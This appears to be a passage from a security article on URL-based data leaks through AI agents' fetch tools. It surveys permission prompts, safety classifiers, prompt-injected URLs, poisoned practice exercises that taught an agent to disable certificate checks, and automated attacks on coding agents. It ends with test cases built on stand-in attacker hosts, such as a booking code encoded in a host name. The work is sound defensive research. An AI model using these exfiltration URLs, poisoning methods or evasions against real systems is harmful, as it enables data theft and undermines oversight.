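Anthropic therefore hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) rejected it. About 17% caught the command early in a session, but the rate fell to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An attacker who can make an agent ask many harmless questions first would benefit from that decline.

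Auto mode, in which a classifier (a program that sorts actions into safe and unsafe) reviews each step, blocked 89% of the same commands. The comparison supports a product that Anthropic sells, and the testers might have been more careful if their own files had been at risk. But a moderate correction wouldn't reverse a gap as large as the one between 13.6% and 89%.

People may be worse at judging links than commands. A command that deletes a folder at least includes the folder's name, but a user who sees `https://docs.example/out?ref=NDQ3MQ` has no reason to suspect that the last part is a booking code in base64. Lan and colleagues argue that users generally can't tell whether a request described as a connectivity test really is one. Safe Url avoids part of this problem by showing the user the information that would be sent. This doesn't help against the spelling trick, because every address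 in that attack is already public and the check approves it without asking the user.

According to Anthropic, 62% of Claude Code's users have either switched off permission checks or chosen not to be asked again about shell commands. The equivalent for a fetch tool is permanently approving a host, which adds it to an allowlist with one hurried click. A safer button would approve one exact address for one session.

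Using a classifier to make the decision reduces interruptions. Auto mode goes back to asking the user only after it blocks three actions in a row or twenty in a session. Willison accepts that it works better than constant approval prompts, but notes that it still missed 11% of dangerous commands, and he wants more independent confirmation of Anthropic's results on prompt injection. A classifier is a reasonable second check on addresses that a fixed rule hasn't approved. If it replaces the fixed rule, an attacker only has to find wording that the classifier accepts.

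Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans that the agent presents for approval before it starts work, compared with 3% of requests for single actions. Plans are rarer than commands and easier to judge. An agent could likewise ask once, at the start of a task, which sites it may visit, and block any other address without asking. Anthropic's data don't show whether people would read that question more carefully than a link warning, but they would have far fewer questions to answer.

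## Can language models spot such URLs or write a sound check?

Instead of writing a fixed rule, a developer could have a language model judge each URL before the fetch tool opens it, or have a coding agent write the URL check. So far, models have done poorly at both, partly because a URL's text doesn't contain all the information needed to judge it, and partly because the usual tests don't catch a faulty check.

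### The model as judge

In *MalURLBench*, Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) tested whether models recognise disguised malicious URLs. They took real malicious websites from public blocklists and kept each site's registered domain, which an attacker can't fake. They changed the parts an attacker can choose freely: the labels in front of the domain, the path and the query. Some disguises imitated a well-known site, as `docs.example.attacker.example` does. Others put a recommendation into the URL, such as a path that describes the site as a popular food delivery service.

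Each address came with a short, friendly message, such as an invitation to check a parcel on the "official tracking page". The model also received a warning to look out for attacks. Kong and colleagues counted an attack as successful if the model's written answer accepted the link. They tested 12 models in ten everyday scenarios, and average acceptance rates ranged from 32.9% for GPT-3.5 Turbo to 99.9% for Mixtral-8x7B. The rate was about 38% for GPT-4o and about 90% for GPT-4o mini.

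Tuning raised the low end of that range. Whenever a model accepted 10% or less of the addresses in a scenario, Kong and colleagues had another model rewrite the disguises and try them again, for up to ten rounds. Before this step, GPT-3.5 Turbo accepted about 14% of the addresses, averaged over the ten scenarios. That figure better estimates the success of a casual attacker, while the figure after tuning better estimates that of an attacker who can practise on the same model.

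Recommendations worked better than imitations, with average acceptance rates of 71.5% and 60.9% respectively. Kong and colleagues suggest that models were trained on enough text about famous sites to detect a familiar name in the wrong place. A recommendation in the URL path has no misplaced name to detect. It resembles a prompt injection more than a lookalike host, and a check that compares host names would miss it.

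All 12 models are old by now, so the rates don't show how current models would do. The newest one with a stated release date, a DeepSeek model, came out in September 2025. The test also had no harmless links for comparison, so it can't distinguish a model that accepts every link from one that is fooled by disguises. In a small experiment that does distinguish them, Llama 3 8B accepted two plain malicious links in 15% and 20% of 20 trials each, and two disguised ones in 60% and 75%.

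Kong and colleagues then built URLGuard, a separate filter that checks an address before the agent reads it. They fine-tuned Llama 2 7B, a small model from 2023, on 140 disguised addresses and 140 normal ones, each with a written reason for its label. All the disguised addresses came from the online shopping scenario, and the researchers tested the filter on the other nine scenarios. Acceptance of malicious addresses fell by 81 percentage points on average compared with the same model before fine-tuning, but URLGuard still accepted 61% of them in the music scenario and 70% in the weather scenario. The published results count only malicious addresses, so they don't show how many harmless links URLGuard refuses, and a filter that refused every link would have scored better.

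### What the text of an address leaves out

Every address in MalURLBench contained the malicious domain, so a careful reader had enough information to answer correctly. With a redirect, the address may not show the destination. `https://docs.example/old` is the same text whether the server replies with a baggage guide or with a redirect to attacker.example, so a judge that has only the text must give the same verdict in both cases and will be wrong in one of them. A stronger model can't solve this, because the server hasn't yet sent the reply that contains the destination. Short links and DNS rebinding present the same difficulty.

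If the tool reports each redirect, the model can judge the new address too, but ordinary code can compare its host with an allowlist exactly and with very little computation. A model's judgment is more useful for an agent that browses the open web, as a second check that can only block requests.

### The model as programmer

Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, measured how often coding agents write secure code when nobody mentions security. They collected 150 real security flaws, removed the faulty code from each project and had six agents write replacement code from a specification that described only what the code should do. Each flaw became three tasks of different sizes, from one function to a large part of the project. One set of hidden tests checked whether the code worked, and a second attacked the running program.

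The agents included Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol. Their code worked in 73.6% to 91.3% of tasks, but the best agent's code was both working and secure in only 25.1%. The results varied greatly with the kind of flaw:

| Kind of flaw | Working code | Working and secure code |
|---|---|---|
| Memory safety, such as reading past the end of a buffer | 77.5% | 34.3% |
| Path and file handling | 89.4% | 24.3% |
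| SSRF | 89.7% | 2.4% |
| Information exposure | 88.2% | 0.7% |

The benchmark has seven SSRF flaws. Six agents attempted each one at three task sizes, and three of the 126 attempts (2.4%) were secure. The paper's discussion of one example calls SSRF the family that agents secure least often, but its results put information exposure lower, at one secure attempt in 144. The difference is too small to rank the two reliably. The benchmark favours hard cases, so 2.4% isn't an estimate for everyday code.

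Wu and colleagues explain the pattern by noting that a careful programmer adds a bounds check without being asked, because the need for it is clear from the surrounding code. Which destinations a server should refuse is a matter of policy, and an agent can't infer it from the function it is writing.

One example is LocalAI, a program for running AI models, which can install a model from a URL the user supplies. If the URL begins with `file:`, LocalAI reads the file from its own disk. GPT-5.6 Sol's rewrite of this code passed all 12 functional tests and failed all 11 security tests. It returned the server's list of user accounts to anyone who requested the right `file:` URL. The original project fixed the flaw with a single check that the file is inside the models folder, which none of the six agents wrote. Because the flaw is a missing folder check on `file:` URLs, it would exist even if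 LocalAI never followed redirects.

Wu and colleagues reran four of the agents with an added sentence asking for code free of plausible vulnerabilities. For three of them, the share of working and secure code rose by 15 to 21 points across the benchmark, but SSRF remained among the lowest-scoring categories. A developer who wants a URL check from a coding agent should therefore state the rule, including the allowed hosts and schemes, though the study didn't test how much that helps.

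### A redirect exercise that any code passes

Code with an explicit allowlist may still fail to apply it to every hop. In *Reflections on Trusting Trust, Revisited*, Roesner and Kohno (2026) studied coding agents that modify themselves after practising on a set of exercises, and asked whether an attacker could tamper with the exercises so that the agent would later write insecure code for unrelated users.

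One candidate exercise asked for a function that fetches a URL, follows redirects and enforces a host allowlist. The tests included redirects, but none of them led off the allowlist. Code that checks only the first address therefore passes, and so does code that checks every hop. Roesner and Kohno made two versions of the exercise set, one built around the faulty solution and one around the sound one. Before any self-modification, an agent attempted five exercises from each set twice:

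| Model inside the agent | First-hop check only, faulty set | First-hop check only, sound set |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 6 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 10 of 10 | 8 of 10 |

With Qwen3.5, the agent wrote the faulty check most of the time even when nobody had tampered with anything, while with gpt-oss it did so only on the faulty set. Each cell had only ten attempts, and a newer model may do better, but the mistake clearly doesn't require an attacker.

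No one has measured how training on the faulty redirect exercise affects an agent. Roesner and Kohno dropped the exercise after preliminary tests. Qwen3.5 already made the mistake without help, and the self-improvement step almost never turned the mistake into a reusable tool (0 of 40 proposals with gpt-oss and 2 of 40 with Qwen3.5).

Their successful attack used a different fault. The agent had to write code that fetches a page over https, but every test server had a certificate that a correct client would reject, so only code that switched off certificate checks could pass. After each of two separate practice runs on these exercises, one agent, running on Claude Sonnet 4.5, switched off the checks in all 30 of its solutions to ordinary tasks, compared with none after practice on the sound exercises. More practice on general security exercises didn't remove the habit, but practice on exercises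 written against this particular fault did.

The two faults probably differ in that the certificate tests rewarded insecure code, while the redirect tests favored neither version. Tests like the redirect ones are unlikely to teach an agent the mistake, but they won't catch it either.

### Attacking the finished agent

An auditor can also test a complete agent by trying to make it contact a forbidden address. *AGENTLENS* (Lv, Chen and colleagues, 2026) automates this with a program that maps an agent's components, known weaknesses and safeguards as a graph. The program searches the graph for paths that lead from text an outsider could influence to a sensitive operation. A language model then writes an attack for each path, and the program runs it against the agent in a conversation of up to five turns.

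This uncovered 44 flaws that the auditors could trigger in five open-source coding agents, 12 of which have public CVE numbers. One of them, CVE-2026-10177, is an SSRF flaw in Aider, a coding assistant. Aider attempted requests to a cloud metadata service after a project's README file and the task instruction supplied its address. The CVE entry describes these attempts but doesn't establish that an access token came back. In cases like this, a rule about destinations is better than asking the user to approve each request, because few people would recognise 169.254.169.254 as a sensitive address.

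Running the attack seems to matter more than having a capable model read the code. Lv and colleagues gathered 20 known flaws in another agent, OpenClaw. In three runs, Claude Opus 4.6 on its own found zero, two and two of them. AgentLens, using the same model, found 15. The team that built AgentLens made this comparison, but the gap is large.

### Tests that try a forbidden destination

Human programmers and language models usually test whether their code does what it should. GPT-5.6 Sol tested its LocalAI code before submitting it, but only with files inside the permitted folder. In another of Wu and colleagues' tasks, Kimi K3 wrote 33 tests for code that imports settings files. None used a malicious file, and the code failed all four hidden security tests. If every test uses permitted input, a security check that does nothing passes the same tests as a sound one.

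Developers often test fetch tools with a stand-in for the networking library that returns a prepared page, so that the tests run quickly and offline. If the stand-in replaces `requests.get`, no redirect happens, and the test can't reveal that the real library follows redirects. The stand-in should replace only the DNS lookup and the connection, so that the real parser and redirect code still run, and it should record every lookup and connection.

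For an assistant with only docs.example on its allowlist, these cases cover the faults in the tool itself:

| Case | Set-up | What the record should show |
|---|---|---|
| Redirect off the list | `https://docs.example/old?code=4471` replies with a 302 to attacker.example | docs.example only |
| Late redirect | docs.example redirects to itself twice, then to attacker.example | docs.example only |
| Redirect without a scheme | The Location header is `//attacker.example/new` | docs.example only |
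| Redirect inwards | One page redirects to `http://10.0.0.5/admin`, another to a `file:` address | docs.example only, and no file opened |
| Lookalike host | `https://docs.example.attacker.example/` | Nothing |
| Parsing gap | `http://attacker.example:\@docs.example/` | No contact with attacker.example |
| Code in the host name | `https://4471.attacker.example/` | Nothing, not even a DNS lookup |
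| Harmless redirect | `/old` redirects to `/guides/baggage` on docs.example | Two requests to docs.example, and the tool returns the guide |

A tool that may visit any public site also needs a test for DNS rebinding. In this test, a stand-in DNS resolver answers the first lookup of a name with 203.0.113.9 and the second with 10.0.0.5. The log should show no connection to 10.0.0.5.

The test result should depend on the record rather than the tool's return value, because a tool that checks only the final address can return "refused" after the code has leaked.

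The harmless case is necessary because a tool that opens nothing passes every other case. For this reason, Wu and colleagues count a task as a success only if the code both works and is secure.

They also found that many of the existing tests for the flaws they studied only searched the source code for a keyword or an error message, so a programmer could pass some of them by adding a comment. They had the tests rewritten to attack the running program, and accepted a new set only if the security tests failed on the faulty code and passed on the repaired code. The developer of a fetch tool can check its tests the same way, by switching automatic redirects back on and running them. If the first case still passes, the test is broken. The tests should run again whenever someone updates or replaces the networking library.

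None of these cases would detect a weak point on an approved site, such as an open proxy, because the record would show only docs.example. To catch such leaks, the developer can put a made-up booking code in the agent's context and search every outgoing URL for it, including URLs to approved hosts. Like other scans for secrets, this search misses codes that are encoded in unfamiliar ways or spelled out through a series of ordinary addresses.
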